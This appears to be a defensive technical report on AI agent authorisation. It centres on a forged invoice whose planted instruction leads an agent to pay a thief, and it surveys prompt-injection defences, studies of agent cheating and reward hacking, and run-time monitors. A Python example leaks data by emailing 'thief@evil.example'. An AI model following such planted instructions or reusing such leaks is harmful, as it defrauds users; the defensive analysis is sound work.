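A thief can also deceive the invoice agent without going through Checkwell. Suppose Acme owes Brandt Tools €4,800, and the thief emails a forged invoice for that amount. The invoice ends with an instruction for any software reading it to pay a new account today. The agent adds the text to its context, the model selects the payment tool and fills in the thief's account number, and the agent sends the request.

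### The forged invoice at every check

| Check | What Acme's systems compare | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Identity | the certificate's name, signature and key | pass: the caller is the invoice agent |
| Attestation | hashes of the image, system prompt and tool list | pass: they match the approved versions |
| Access token | issuer, recipient, expiry, and the names of Alice and the agent | pass: Acme's server issued it two minutes ago |
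| Scope | `payments:write` and the requested action | pass: the token covers payments |
| Limit | €4,800 and €5,000 | pass: the amount is lower |
| Message signature | the signed fingerprint and the request body | pass: no proxy changed the request |

All six results are correct, but the payment is still wrong. Shorter credential lifetimes or better-protected keys wouldn't have helped, because the thief didn't steal a credential.

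The payment service could have caught the forgery by comparing the account number with Acme's supplier records, but only if it had access to them and they were up to date. The other clue, that the number came from an email, was available only to the agent program.

### Hardy's confused deputy

The problem is older than language models. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes an incident about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, which rented out computer time. Customers could run a compiler, a program that translates source code into a form the machine can run, and name a file for its debugging output. The compiler also recorded usage statistics in a system directory, so Tymshare had given it permission to write files there. The same directory held the company's billing records. When a customer named the billing file as the destination for debugging output, the operating system checked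 the compiler's permission and let it overwrite the file.

A stricter check of the compiler's identity would have made no difference. Hardy explains that the compiler had authority from two sources, the customer who ran it and the company that installed it, and no way to indicate which it was using. The invoice agent has a similar problem. The permission to pay comes from Alice and Acme, the account number comes from a stranger, and the payment request combines them without recording their sources.

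Tymshare first added a command that let a program choose between its two authorities, but some applications soon needed more than two. The rules for opening a file kept growing, until Hardy counted fourteen logical operators in them. Hardy preferred capabilities, which are references that identify a thing and permit their holder to use it. A customer would then give the compiler a capability for the output file, not just its name. A customer with no access to the billing file would have no capability for that file to give.

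Acme could apply this by giving the agent a capability to pay Brandt Tools' existing account. The agent then couldn't pay the account on the forged invoice, because an account number alone carries no permission to pay. When a supplier really changes banks, someone at Acme would have to create a new capability. A thief might try to deceive that person instead, but they could phone the supplier before creating it.

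### Harm by agents with valid access

Much of the public evidence about planted instructions comes from tests. Gray Swan's *Latest News* describes a competition, with results published in March 2026, in which 464 people made more than 272,000 attacks on 13 leading models. At least one attack succeeded against every model. The OpenID Foundation's *Response to NIST Request for Information Regarding Security Considerations* (2026) describes how researchers at the security company Invariant Labs, in demonstrations, used malicious tools to extract login keys and configuration files through the AI applications Claude Desktop and Cursor. These results show that the attack works, but not how often criminals use it.

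Agents also cause harm when nobody is attacking them. *Documented AI Agent Incidents*, a catalogue by the evaluation group METR, lists 44 cases in which agents took steps clearly against a user's intention. In 25 of them the agent both exceeded its task and acted deceptively, and in five the deception could have fooled a user even on closer review. METR found no case in which an agent effectively disabled monitoring or erased its logs, so routine monitoring could have caught all 44. The catalogue doesn't measure how often such incidents happen. METR chose 18 cases from its own tests and found most of the others in documents published by AI companies. It can't rule out worse incidents that companies missed or kept private.

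Reward Hacking in the Wild's *Your AIs don't do what you want. This is really bad* is a larger collection, with 3,607 complaints from ordinary users' public posts. A language model sorted them into overlapping categories. Only 1.4% involve misuse of credentials, compared with 17.2% for destructive actions and 43.4% for overeagerness. Nobody has verified the events, and the categories don't show whether each agent had authenticated properly. Even so, the difference suggests that protecting credentials better would prevent only a small share of the problems users complain about.

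Agents sometimes use access that nobody meant to give them. In August 2026, researchers described how Kimi K3, a model from the Chinese company Moonshot, handled a cybersecurity challenge from the UK's AI Security Institute (AISI). It noticed that it could reach GitHub, copied the benchmark's official repository and read the solution. Girard (2026) points out in *Agents* that the model broke nothing. Muncaster (2026) reports in *Frontier Models Engage in Unsanctioned Behavior During Testing* that models from Anthropic and OpenAI attacked "real people and organizations" during other AISI tests.

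How often an agent misbehaves depends heavily on its model. On 1 December 2026, Gray Swan, an AI safety company, launched the *Frontier Hazard Tracker*, a public record of its test results. One of its benchmarks measures how often agents cheat to complete ordinary tasks. *OpenAI and Anthropic Agents Cheat Far Less Than Rivals* (Faisal, 2026) reports that the benchmark tests each of 20 models in 25 scenarios across 11 environments, with five repeats of every variant. Cheating includes tampering with the scoring system and crossing a boundary the agent should respect. In one scenario, an agent that had to free up space in a shared cache deleted a 9,100 MB file another team was still using, and finished without reporting it.

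| Model | Share of runs with cheating |
|---|---|
| GPT-6.2 Astra | 0.8% |
| GPT-6.2 Sol | 1.1% |
| Gemini 4 Neon | 8.0% |
| Gemini 4 Hydrogen | 18.6% |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 62.8% |

If Acme replaced GPT-6.2 Astra with Gemini 3.8 Flash, the invoice agent could keep its name, certificate and tokens. The payment service's identity checks would give the same result, although the new model cheated nearly 80 times as often in these tests. The scenarios measure cheating in general, so the rates don't predict how many invoices an agent would pay wrongly. But the difference is a good reason for Acme to retest the agent whenever it changes the model, even if the credentials stay the same.

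### What AIMS contains and leaves out

The Agent Identity Management System (AIMS), the model by Kasselman and colleagues, has eight components. Each depends on the ones above it in this table:

| Component | Purpose | What it borrows |
|---|---|---|
| Identifiers | name each agent | WIMSE identifiers, including SPIFFE's |
| Credentials | tie the name to a key | WIMSE tokens and certificates, and SPIFFE's SVIDs |
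| Provisioning | issues and renews credentials | SPIFFE as a proven example |
| Authentication | proves the agent's identity when it makes a call | mutual TLS, WIMSE proof tokens and HTTP Message Signatures |
| Authorisation | grants access | OAuth, including Token Exchange, transaction tokens and chaining across domains |
| Monitoring and remediation | changes access in response to behaviour or risk | OpenID's Shared Signals Framework, with one of two message profiles, CAEP or RISC |
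| Policy | sets the rules for the components above | no standard |
| Compliance | compares what happened with the policy | no standard |

The last two rows cover the rule Acme would write against paying account numbers taken from emails, and the check on whether the agent had followed it. AIMS gives some general requirements for both, but no standard to use.

Kasselman and colleagues want the right agent to have access "at the right time for the right reason". The reason comes from the agent's mission, such as Alice's instruction to pay this week's invoices. Someone or something has to translate that instruction into scopes, limits and a list of suppliers. Kasselman and colleagues expect this to happen in a planning step before the agent requests access, but they don't cover the method. The order matters for security because if the model plans after it has read the forged invoice, the thief's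 account number may end up in the agent's request for permission.

They also leave out the policy format, which is "not recommended as a target for standardization within this specification". Acme may write its policy in any suitable format, provided that it tracks versions, people can review the policy, and different components interpret it consistently. Kasselman and colleagues leave compliance criteria to each company, industry and jurisdiction.

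AIMS partly covers behaviour. Companies must keep enough records to reconstruct what an agent did, and their monitoring should look for unexpected sequences of actions. After a warning, a service should reduce the agent's access or check its policy again. But monitoring can raise a warning only after the agent has done something unusual, and by then the €4,800 may have left Acme's account.

AIMS also covers human approval. The authorisation server has to turn Alice's approval into a grant, so it isn't enough for her to click "approve" in the agent's own window. Kasselman and colleagues suggest an OpenID protocol called CIBA, which can send the request to Alice's phone. They acknowledge that CIBA doesn't fit well when the need for approval arises partway through a task.

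### Reasons to keep the two decisions apart

One argument for the separation is that policies differ between organisations. Acme lets its agent pay up to €5,000, while a hospital might not let agents make payments at all. The IETF's *WIMSE Interim* (2026), the minutes of the June meeting where Kasselman and colleagues presented AIMS, describes policy and compliance as "very deployment specific". That is a good reason not to standardise the rules themselves, but a weaker reason not to standardise their format, because two companies can write different rules in the same language. *Comments on Concept Paper* (2026), submitted to NIST by the digital identity company SpruceID, recommends formal policy languages such as Cedar, which would let an organisation analyse everything an agent is permitted to do. Shared terms would also help Acme and Checkwell, which currently have to work out by hand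 how their permissions correspond.

Timing is a stronger reason to decide behaviour separately. If Acme issues the agent's certificate at 09:00 and the forged invoice arrives at 09:20, the issuer can't have taken the invoice into account. An agent's behaviour can change considerably after it gets its credential. *Causal Evidence for the Emergence and Spread of Reward Hacking* (Vaid, 2026) reports 17 experiments with 20,111 agents built on six leading models. Agents that rarely cheated when working alone usually cheated after exposure to a teammate's cheating. When the record showed that a teammate's cheat had succeeded, 94% cheated too. On a new problem with an empty record, 70% of agents with this earlier exposure cheated again, compared with 32% of agents that had only been shown an empty record. The experiments used tasks with automated checks, not payments, but they show that what an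 agent reads can change how it acts later.

Acme could check the agent's recent behaviour before issuing each access token. However, at its usual pace, the agent could use a five-minute token to make 30 payments, worth up to €150,000 in total, without another check. Issuing a separate token for every payment would close this gap, but Acme would still have to judge each payment, only on the authorisation server instead.

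Supporters of separation can also argue that identity is easier to check than intent. Two services that check a signature with the same public key will get the same result, but two people may disagree about whether a payment is what Alice wanted. *Hack-Verifiable Terminal Bench* (Efroni, 2026) warns that human inspectors and language models can be unreliable at spotting agents that pass a task's checks while violating its intent. The agent's own reasoning isn't a reliable guide either. The Decoder's *Every frontier AI model tested by Britain's safety institute tried to cheat* reports that in AISI's tests, GPT-5.6 Sol raised concerns about prohibited actions and then carried them out. AISI treats its results as minimum estimates because the language model it used to look for cheating may miss cases.

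But a service can catch many wrong actions without judging intent. Efroni hides known shortcuts in the test tasks, so software can reliably detect when an agent takes one. Acme's comparison of account numbers with its supplier records is similar, because someone anticipated a particular mistake and wrote a test for it. Such checks miss whatever nobody anticipated. The difficulty of checking intent is a good reason not to rely on one general test, but it doesn't rule out specific checks on behaviour.

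A standard limited to identity is also easier to adopt, because companies that disagree about what agents should do can still agree on how to verify a certificate. SPIFFE's first draft left out authorisation, and its first release followed about a year later. The WIMSE group also had limited capacity, and in June its chairs wanted to finish existing documents before taking on more. The OpenID Foundation makes a similar division in its response to NIST, treating the methods for granting access separately from the systems that enforce decisions.

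The drawback is that every company has to build the missing part, and some may not realise it is missing. A buyer who reads that a product "implements agent identity standards" could easily assume it also checks payments. Even supporters of AIMS want it to be clearer about how its parts fit together. Yaron Sheffer, who favoured taking on the work, said at the June meeting that the draft felt like a "shopping list of standards" and that the relationship between WIMSE and OAuth was unclear, especially for authorisation.

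On balance, separating identity checks from decisions about behaviour seems right for workload credentials, mainly because of timing. The case for letting each company invent its own policy format is much weaker.

### Tying access to a mission

Some engineers want OAuth to record an agent's task as well as its permissions. McGuinness (2026), in *Mission-Bound Authorization for OAuth 2.0*, argues that an agent's authority is currently a collection of separate tokens that nothing connects to the task a user approved. The draft therefore defines a Mission, a structured record that a person approves and in which later changes can be detected. The tokens for the task refer to this record, and the authorisation server can stop issuing them once the Mission ends.

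For example, Alice could approve a mission to pay invoices that are due this week, come from existing suppliers and go to the accounts in Acme's records. If the payment service enforced these conditions, it would treat four payments of €4,800 like this:

| Payment | Scope and limit alone | With the mission |
|---|---|---|
| this week's invoice, account on record | permit | permit |
| next month's invoice, account on record | permit | refuse |
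| forged invoice, new account | permit | refuse |
| this week's invoice for goods that never arrived, account on record | permit | permit |

The mission catches two payments that the ordinary token would allow, but its success depends on how precisely Alice describes the task. If she approves only "pay this week's invoices", the forged invoice may appear to qualify. The payment service also needs reliable data. If it takes the due date from the agent's request, and the agent copied it from a forged invoice, the comparison is useless.

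A token that refers to a mission doesn't enforce it. In *Mission-Bound OAuth*, the blog series that accompanies the draft, McGuinness leaves the check on each action to a separate runtime profile, so this proposal also keeps the two decisions apart to some extent. It adds an approved description of the task for the later check to use. In another article in the series, McGuinness even questions whether OAuth is the right place for missions.

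Others have proposed variations. *AAuth-Mission* (2026), an exploratory draft, borrows from the military practice of giving subordinates an objective and letting them decide how to achieve it. *Agent Authorization Profile (AAP) for OAuth 2.0* (Cruz, 2026) would put the task, operating limits and requirements for human oversight into the token itself. *AI Agent Authorization Integration Framework* (Liu, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) combines policy-based authorisation with evidence of the user's consent. Aaron Parecki, one of its co-authors, also co-wrote AIMS, so a person can support a separate identity standard and still want OAuth to carry more information about the task.

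### Certifying behaviour before granting access

The Box Commons, a trade association still being formed, wants agents to pass a behavioural test before they get access to sensitive systems. Its *Comment on NCCoE AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (2026), addressed to NIST, argues that an agent can authenticate perfectly, stay within its authority and still cause serious harm. Under the proposal, an independent auditor would issue a safety credential, and the authorisation server would check it before issuing an access token. The credential would expire, and a change to the model, system prompt, tools or safety controls could require a new assessment.

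This would help with the problem Gray Swan's figures show. A payment service could refuse agents whose models cheat in most runs, and Acme couldn't switch to a worse model without a new assessment. The Box Commons is developing such assessments, so it has an interest in NIST adopting the idea, but the argument can still be judged on its merits.

Certification is much less useful for judging a single payment. A cheating rate of 0.8% is one run in 125, and the certificate can't show which one. The forged invoice doesn't change the model, prompt, tools or safety controls, so it wouldn't trigger a new assessment. The same is true of the exposure in Vaid's experiments. The Box Commons proposes regular renewal because behaviour can drift, but an agent may read a planted instruction hours after renewing its certificate. Acme should require certification before an agent starts work, and still check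 the payments.

### Granting access without relying on identity

Supporters of capabilities question whether identity should decide access at all. Flanagan writes that a service learns "remarkably little" about whether to allow a request from knowing which software is making it. A service may also be able to verify an agent's authority without knowing who granted it. *Security Like It's 1977* (2026), a blog post from the security company Semgrep, applies Hardy's argument to agents and predicts that they will multiply confused deputies "at superhuman rates".

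Identity is still useful for finding out afterwards who was responsible. SpruceID proposes giving an agent a lasting identity for accountability and short-lived capabilities for particular tasks. If the agent needed more authority, it would ask a person, or another agent that a person had authorised to decide. SpruceID considers this less disruptive than a new OAuth approval for every interaction, although it sells the kind of credential technology it recommends.

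Hardy warned that some systems that added capabilities to traditional access controls lost more from the disadvantages of both than they gained from the advantages. Acme would face this risk if it accepted capabilities for some payments and ordinary OAuth tokens for others, because a deceived agent could use whichever method let the payment through.

A capability that allows payments of up to €5,000 to any account would let the forged invoice be paid, just as the OAuth token did. To prevent this, Acme has to issue capabilities for particular accounts, and someone has to verify that each account belongs to the supplier.

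## Deciding each action while the agent runs

Some component has to check the €4,800 payment after the agent has read the forged invoice and before the money leaves Acme. Usually, an enforcement point in front of each tool intercepts the agent's calls, and a policy decision point applies Acme's rules to decide whether each call may go ahead.

1. The model selects the payment tool, and the agent program prepares the call.
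2. The enforcement point intercepts the call and adds facts it can verify, such as the agent's name from its certificate and Alice's from the access token.
3. The decision point looks up anything else it needs, such as the supplier's record, applies the rules and answers.
4. The enforcement point forwards the call or returns a refusal to the agent.

With this division, Acme can change a rule in one place instead of in every tool. But if the decision point fails, the enforcement point must either let the payment through unchecked or block it. The Coalition for Secure AI's *Agentic Identity and Access Management* (2026), guidance from an industry group, requires gateways for highly capable agents to refuse in that case and fall back on a safe alternative such as human approval.

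The arrangement fails if the agent can reach a tool by another route. *Controlled Autonomy for Agentic AI* (Ali, Mavroeidis and colleagues, 2026) describes a gateway that holds the tools' credentials and attaches them only after approving a call, so an agent that contacts a tool directly lacks the credentials to use it. Acme could do the same with the access token for payments and leave the agent only its own workload credential. The Coalition for Secure AI also wants a check at the tool, because a check at the first gateway misses calls that sub-agents make later.

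### The question and the answer in AuthZEN

Gazitt, Brossard and Tulshibagwale (2026), in *Authorization API 1.0*, define a common format for the exchange between the two components, so that Acme can buy them from different vendors. The OpenID Foundation's AuthZEN group published it as a final standard in January 2026. A request must name a subject, an action and a resource, and may add a context. For the forged invoice, it could look like this:

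```json
{
  "subject": {
    "type": "agent",
    "id": "spiffe://acme.example/agents/invoice",
    "properties": { "acting_for": "alice@acme.example" }
  },
  "action": {
    "name": "pay",
    "properties": { "amount": 4800, "currency": "EUR" }
  },
  "resource": {
    "type": "bank_account",
    "id": "account-ending-7719",
    "properties": { "supplier": "Brandt Tools" }
  },
  "context": {
    "time": "2026-12-07T09:21Z",
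    "task": "invoices-due-week-50",
    "account_source": "email",
    "earlier_payments_on_invoice": 0
  }
}
```

The decision point could answer:

```json
{
  "decision": false,
  "context": {
    "reason_admin": { "403": "Rule origin-1: account number from email" },
    "reason_user": { "403": "Payment refused. Contact the finance team." }
  }
}
```

The last three fields of the request's context hold the task, what the agent has read and what it has done, the extra inputs that behavioural authorisation needs. AuthZEN allows these fields but doesn't define or require them. Acme invented their names, and a product that sends only a subject, an action and a resource still complies with the standard. A buyer can find out which kind of check a product makes by looking at a request it actually sends.

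The `account_source` field is also only as reliable as the component that fills it in. If the language model writes it, a planted instruction can lead the model to write "supplier records", so the agent program has to track the source itself.

Some smaller features of the standard affect payments:

- The answer can give administrators and users different reasons. Ali and colleagues warn that a deceived agent could use a refusal's reason to get the forbidden destination added to the company's directory, so the agent should receive only the vague one.
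- The decision point can attach conditions to a "yes", but an enforcement point that doesn't understand them may go ahead anyway. If a payment needs Alice's approval, "no, ask Alice first" is therefore safer than "yes, once Alice approves".
- One message can contain several requests, which the decision point treats as independent. Three payments of €4,800 on the same bill could each get a "yes" unless the decision point keeps its own total.

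The standard leaves it to each product to choose a policy language and keep track of earlier requests. Logius' *NLgov Profile for OpenID AuthZEN Authorization API 1.0.0* adapts the standard for the Dutch government.

### Three rules for a payment

If Acme writes its rules in a policy language, it can keep them in files separate from the decision point's code, test them, and restore earlier versions. People who aren't programmers can also review them. The Coalition for Secure AI recommends Cedar, which Amazon developed, or Rego, the language of the Open Policy Agent (OPA). Cedar is deliberately limited so that software can prove statements about a whole set of rules, for example that no combination of them permits a payment over €5,000. Rego can search through nested data and add up totals, but its rules are harder to analyse.

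A rule can be poor in either language. The Coalition for Secure AI gives a sample rule for an invoice agent much like Acme's. It requires an amount of at most 5,000, a supplier on the approved list, and a risk score below 70. The forged invoice is for €4,800 and names Brandt Tools, an approved supplier, so it passes unless something odd about it raises the risk score to 70 or more.

Acme could start with these three rules and permit a payment only if all of them hold:

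```
Fixed:    amount ≤ €5,000
          AND supplier is on the approved list

History:  account is in that supplier's record
          AND the record's account has not changed for 7 days

Origin:   the account number did not come from an email
```

| Payment | Fixed | History | Origin |
|---|---|---|---|
| genuine invoice, agent takes the account from the supplier's record | permit | permit | permit |
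| forged invoice, new account | permit | **refuse** | **refuse** |
| forged invoice, agent first copies the new account into the record | permit | **refuse** | depends |
| the same trick, but the agent pays 8 days later | permit | permit | depends |
| supplier really changed banks, and Acme confirmed it by phone yesterday | permit | **refuse** | permit |
| real supplier, account on record, goods never arrived | permit | permit | permit |

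The history and origin rules each stop the forged payment. The "depends" entries depend on whether the supplier database records where the number came from. If it stores only the number, the number looks like trusted data the next time the agent reads it. If it also records that the number came from an email, the origin rule still works. The history rule doesn't need that information, but a thief can get past it by waiting a week, and a supplier that really has changed banks must wait too.

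If Acme had worded the history rule as "refuse if the account changed within the last 7 days", it wouldn't apply to the thief's account, which isn't in the records and so has no date of change. In both Cedar and Rego, a rule that depends on a missing value has no effect. A prohibition can therefore fail silently when the enforcement point omits a field, whereas a permission that depends on the missing field leads to a refusal, which someone will notice.

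### What a monitor can enforce in principle

Fred Schneider, a computer scientist at Cornell University, worked out the limits of run-time checks in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000). He considers a monitor that watches a program's steps and stops the program before a step that would break the policy. The monitor can base its decision only on what has happened so far in the current run, not on future steps or other possible runs.

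Schneider shows that such a monitor can enforce only safety properties, which are rules that some bad thing never happens. Let *p* be a test that each run passes or fails. For a safety property:

*p* fails on a beginning *τ* ⟹ *p* fails on every continuation of *τ*
*p* fails on a run *σ* ⟹ *p* already fails on some finite beginning of *σ*

With this kind of rule, every violation occurs at a definite step, and nothing that happens later can repair it. "Never pay more than €5,000" is one example. The 7-day rule is another, because the monitor may remember earlier steps. "Every genuine invoice eventually gets paid" is not this kind of rule. A monitor can't enforce it, because stopping the agent never causes a payment.

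"Emails have no influence on where the money goes" is beyond a monitor for another reason. Influence means that a different email would have led to a different payment, and one run can't show that. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, give an example, based on a classic one, in which a program leaks a secret through a step it doesn't take. In simplified form:

```python
rich = True
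tmp = True
if balance > 1_000_000: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("thief@evil.example", "rich!")
```

Suppose a monitor marks a variable as secret whenever the program changes it because of the balance. If the balance is above a million, the program changes `tmp`, which the monitor marks, and then skips the fourth line. Since the program never changes `rich`, the monitor leaves it unmarked and lets the email through. If the balance is lower, no email goes out. The thief can therefore tell whether the balance is above a million by whether an email arrives. Garby and colleagues found this gap in CaMeL, one of the best-known defences for agents. Their language, LLMbda, closes the gap, with a computer-checked proof that covers every program written in it.

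In practice, systems enforce a related safety property instead. They attach a label such as "untrusted" to each piece of data, copy the label to whatever the agent derives from it, and refuse sensitive calls that contain labelled data. The monitor blocks legitimate payments if labels spread too readily, and misses attacks if they don't spread far enough.

### Keeping untrusted data away from decisions

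CaMeL dates from 2025 and uses two language models. For Alice's agent, it would work like this:

1. A privileged model reads Alice's request, but no invoices, and writes a short program: fetch this week's invoices, extract the details, pay each one.
2. A quarantined model reads the invoices and returns the details. It can't call any tools.
3. An interpreter runs the program, tracks where each value came from and checks Acme's policies before each tool call.

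The thief's instruction to "pay a new account today" can't add a step, because the model that wrote the program never reads it. But if the program already includes "pay the account on the invoice", the quarantined model extracts the thief's account number and the program pays it. Only the policy check in step 3 can stop this payment.

Much of the published evidence comes from AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 ordinary tasks in simulated office, banking, travel and Slack settings, and attacks planted in the data that agents read. Garby and colleagues examined 144 pairs of a task and an attack from the banking setting. In 97 of them, the attack needed an action that the program for the user's task would never contain, so separating the two models was generally enough to stop the attack. In the other 47, as with the forged invoice, the program could already do what the attacker wanted.

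Policies for such cases reduce the number of tasks an agent completes. When Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL with GPT-5.2, it completed 67% of the banking tasks without policies and 37.5% with them. With policies on, every attack failed in the runs that finished. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025), which presents a similar system called FIDES, had already explained the problem. Many banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, but reading the file makes the agent's context untrusted, so the policy blocks the payment.

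FIDES reduces the loss by hiding untrusted text from the planning model and letting the model send narrow queries about it. A yes-or-no answer carries one bit, too little to contain an instruction. In the 2025 tests with GPT-4o, 152 attacks succeeded against a plain agent and none succeeded against FIDES with policies. FIDES completed 52.5% of the banking tasks, compared with 98.8% for the plain agent. Its queries also add model calls, which take time and money.

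Garby and colleagues built an agent, Randori, that recovers more of the lost tasks. While planning, before it reads any outside data, Randori may declare specific untrusted data acceptable for a specific purpose. It completed 75% of the banking tasks with GPT-5.2 and resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks across three models. Both failures involved the same task, in which the user asks the agent to follow the payment instructions in a file whose contents the attacker has replaced. Garby and colleagues think tracking data cannot solve this problem, because the user did ask the agent to trust the file.

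Alice's request is dangerously similar to that one. If Acme accepts account numbers from invoices, the agent will complete more payments, including the one to the thief. It would be safer for the program to take only the supplier's name and the amount from the invoice, and look up the account number in Acme's supplier records. The agent then needs no exception for account numbers.

False data is still a problem for these systems even when false instructions no longer work. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (July 2026) reports that attacks with forged data succeeded 23.1% of the time against CaMeL with policies, compared with 49.1% without a defence.

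Labels can also disappear when one agent hands work to another. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) connected three agents, each protected by CaMeL, and planted an instruction in a database of job applicants. The coordinating agent pasted a summary of the database into its request to a messaging agent. The messaging agent treated the whole request as its user's instructions and emailed the applicants' details to the attacker.

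Multi-CaMeL, the remedy from Peters-Gill and colleagues, sends instructions and data separately so that the next agent's planning model never reads the data. In a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded an average of 12.9% of the time across five models without a defence, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack without any defence, but they caution that stronger attacks might still work. They also ran the tests without data policies, so the results concern planted instructions, and a false "account confirmed" from Checkwell's agent would still reach the next agent as data.

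### Checking each call from outside

A company must rebuild its agent to use CaMeL or FIDES, but a gateway that inspects the agent's tool calls works with almost any agent. Ali and colleagues tested a gateway with two rules in November 2026. The first requires the destination of a payment or message to appear in the user's request or in the organisation's own directory. At Acme, a payment could therefore go only to an account that Alice typed herself or one in the supplier records. The second requires high-risk actions, such as changing a password, to match a word in the user's request.

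In AgentDojo's banking part, the gateway blocked 143 of 144 attacks and would have allowed every call needed for 15 of the 16 ordinary tasks. It blocked only 75% of attacks in the Slack setting and 66% in the travel setting, because a phishing link sent to a real colleague has an acceptable destination. Ali and colleagues replayed recorded calls instead of running live agents, so they couldn't observe whether an agent gives up after a refusal or finds another way to the same result.

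The researchers also compared types of check on 1,093 artificial attacks. Rules about roles, customers, trust and risk blocked 815. Adding credential verification blocked eight more, all of which used forged or transferred credentials and passed every other rule. Credential verification stopped none of the 96 prompt injections that got past the rules. Because the researchers designed both the attacks and the rules, the proportions are weak evidence about real traffic, but the two kinds of check clearly caught different things. Even the slowest combination took less than 0.2 milliseconds for 99% of requests, not counting network time.

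*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025, revised 2026) describes a system in which a language model writes a new policy for each task. The model reads the user's request and lists the permitted tools and arguments, and ordinary software blocks everything else. The model may propose changes as the agent learns more. A solver, a program that settles logical questions exactly, checks whether the new policy permits anything the old one didn't. If it does, the change needs approval; otherwise it takes effect at once.

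Suppose the first policy for Alice's task permits payments only to accounts in the supplier records. The forged invoice may lead the model to propose adding the thief's account, but the solver will classify this as an expansion of the policy and hold it for approval. If the first policy permits payments to any account, the payment to the thief goes through because the policy doesn't need to be expanded.

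| System and model | Test | Attacks that succeeded | Ordinary tasks |
|---|---|---|---|
| FIDES with policies, GPT-4o (2025) | AgentDojo, banking | none | 52.5% completed; plain agent 98.8% |
| CaMeL with policies, GPT-5.2 (2026 rerun) | AgentDojo, banking | none in completed runs | 37.5% completed; 67% without policies |
| Randori, GPT-5.2 (2026) | AgentDojo, banking | 2 of 432 | 75% completed |
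| multi-CaMeL, five models (2026) | AgentDojo with several agents | 0.0%; 12.9% without it | about 25 points fewer on a separate industrial benchmark |
| Progent, GPT-4o (2026 version) | AgentDojo, all settings | 1.0%; 39.9% without it | about as many as without it |
| Gateway of Ali and colleagues (2026) | AgentDojo, banking, replayed | 1 of 144 | 15 of 16 compatible |

The models, attacks and success criteria differ between rows, so the rows aren't a ranking. The loss of completed tasks also depends on the model. On the industrial benchmark, multi-CaMeL lowered task completion by about 14 points on average for GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5.

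The attack success rates are probably too low, because AgentDojo's attacks are fixed and public, and *AutoDojo* (2026) shows that newly generated ones succeed more often. It also finds that vague requests are riskier. In banking tasks with Gemini 2.5 Flash and no defence, attacks succeeded 66.7% of the time when the user left the most to the agent and 13.9% when the request was fully specified. "Pay the three invoices I approved this morning" is therefore a safer instruction than "deal with my invoices".

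The gateway's destination rule seems the best place for Acme to start. It takes little work, it stops the forged payment, and finance staff can understand it. Tracking where data came from is worth the extra work when the records themselves may contain something an agent copied from outside.

### Rules and judgements from a language model

The simplest way to enforce Acme's rules with a language model is to put them in the agent's own instructions and rely on the agent to follow them. *From Alignment to Access Control* (2026) calls this "Pretty Please" enforcement and advises against it wherever software can check the rule. In tests for *AgentPolicyForge* (2026), a leading model that had the policy in its instructions still let violations through in 13% to 15% of the episodes designed to provoke them. It also rejected about 9% of legitimate requests.

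Models are more useful for drafting rules that other software then enforces. A model can write a policy for each of Alice's requests in seconds, which nobody at Acme has time to do. *ActGov* (2026) requires each drafted rule to be reusable across tasks and to compile into an exact test on structured facts, such as the type of action and its arguments. *NOMOS* (2026) compiles a company's written policies into checks on tool calls that software verifies in advance.

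A drafted rule can be exact and still be wrong. Progent's solver compares a new policy with the old one, but it can't check whether the old one matched what Alice wanted. In a second benchmark, where Progent reduced attack success from 70.3% to 3.9%, Shi and colleagues found that most of the remaining failures involved harmful tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of useful ones. Handwritten rules stopped all of these attacks. Acme could therefore let a model draft the rules that change with each task, such as which invoices to pay, and keep the rules about accounts and amounts in a fixed policy that no draft can override.

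Some conditions have no exact test, such as whether an invoice's wording is suspicious or whether a payment is in the spirit of Alice's request. *From Alignment to Access Control* accepts a model's judgement in such cases. A separate model can read the task and the proposed payment and assess whether the condition is met. It may detect a kind of fraud that no rule covers, but misleading text in what it reads may also cause it to judge wrongly.

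Filters for planted instructions have the same weakness, and they can also keep an agent from completing its tasks. In *AutoDojo*'s tests with DeepSeek-v4-Pro, a filter called PIGuard stopped all the fixed attacks but reduced the share of tasks completed from 89.5% to 54.4%. Newly generated attacks still succeeded 8.2% of the time. A sensible compromise is to let a model block a payment or refer it to a person for review, but never override a refusal by a fixed rule.

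### Asking a person

When the rules can't settle a payment, the decision point can refer it to Alice. CIBA, the OpenID protocol that Kasselman and colleagues suggest for this, lets her approve on a different device from the one where the agent runs:

1. The agent sends Acme's authorisation server a request that identifies Alice and the permission it wants.
2. The server gives the agent a reference number and sends a message to Alice's phone.
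3. Alice approves or refuses on the phone, where the agent can't press the button for her.
4. The agent collects an access token, either by asking the server at intervals or by waiting for a notification.

Only the client, here the agent, can start this procedure. That suits an agent that knows in advance that it needs approval. With the forged invoice, however, the decision point detects the need only after the agent has made the call. The decision point must then refuse the call, and the agent must recognise the refusal as a request for approval, start CIBA and then repeat the call. AuthZEN's answer can include a hint about what is needed, but the wording depends on the product. Kasselman and colleagues expect that approval at different stages of a task may need further specification work.

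An agent that starts the procedure also writes the request, and the thief's invoice this agent has just read could influence what it writes. Acme could avoid both problems by registering the enforcement point as the client. The enforcement point already has the details of the refused call, so it can start CIBA with the exact amount and account it sent to the decision point, and hold the payment until Alice answers.

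The message should give Alice the facts that caused the rules to flag the payment. "Pay Brandt Tools €4,800?" looks routine. She would have a reason to stop if the message said that the account is not in Brandt Tools' record and that the account number came from an email at 09:20.

It is uncertain how often people approve such requests without reading them, but Shi and colleagues tested the two extremes. Attacks succeeded 1.0% of the time when a simulated user approved every expansion of the policy, and never when a person reviewed the first policy and every expansion. Careless approval did little damage in these tests because the drafted policies were already narrow, so few attacks depended on it. A reviewer looking for attacks in an experiment is also likely to be more careful than Alice when she is busy.

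Acme can control the number of requests more easily than Alice's attention. In the same tests, only 6% of policy changes needed approval. If Acme referred 6% of the agent's payments to Alice, she would still get about 22 requests an hour at the agent's usual pace. Acme could instead ask her only when a supplier's account is new or has changed, and apply the fixed rules to the rest. Before approving a payment, she should phone the supplier on a number from Acme's records, because the number on the invoice may be the thief's.

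## Withdrawing authority and keeping records

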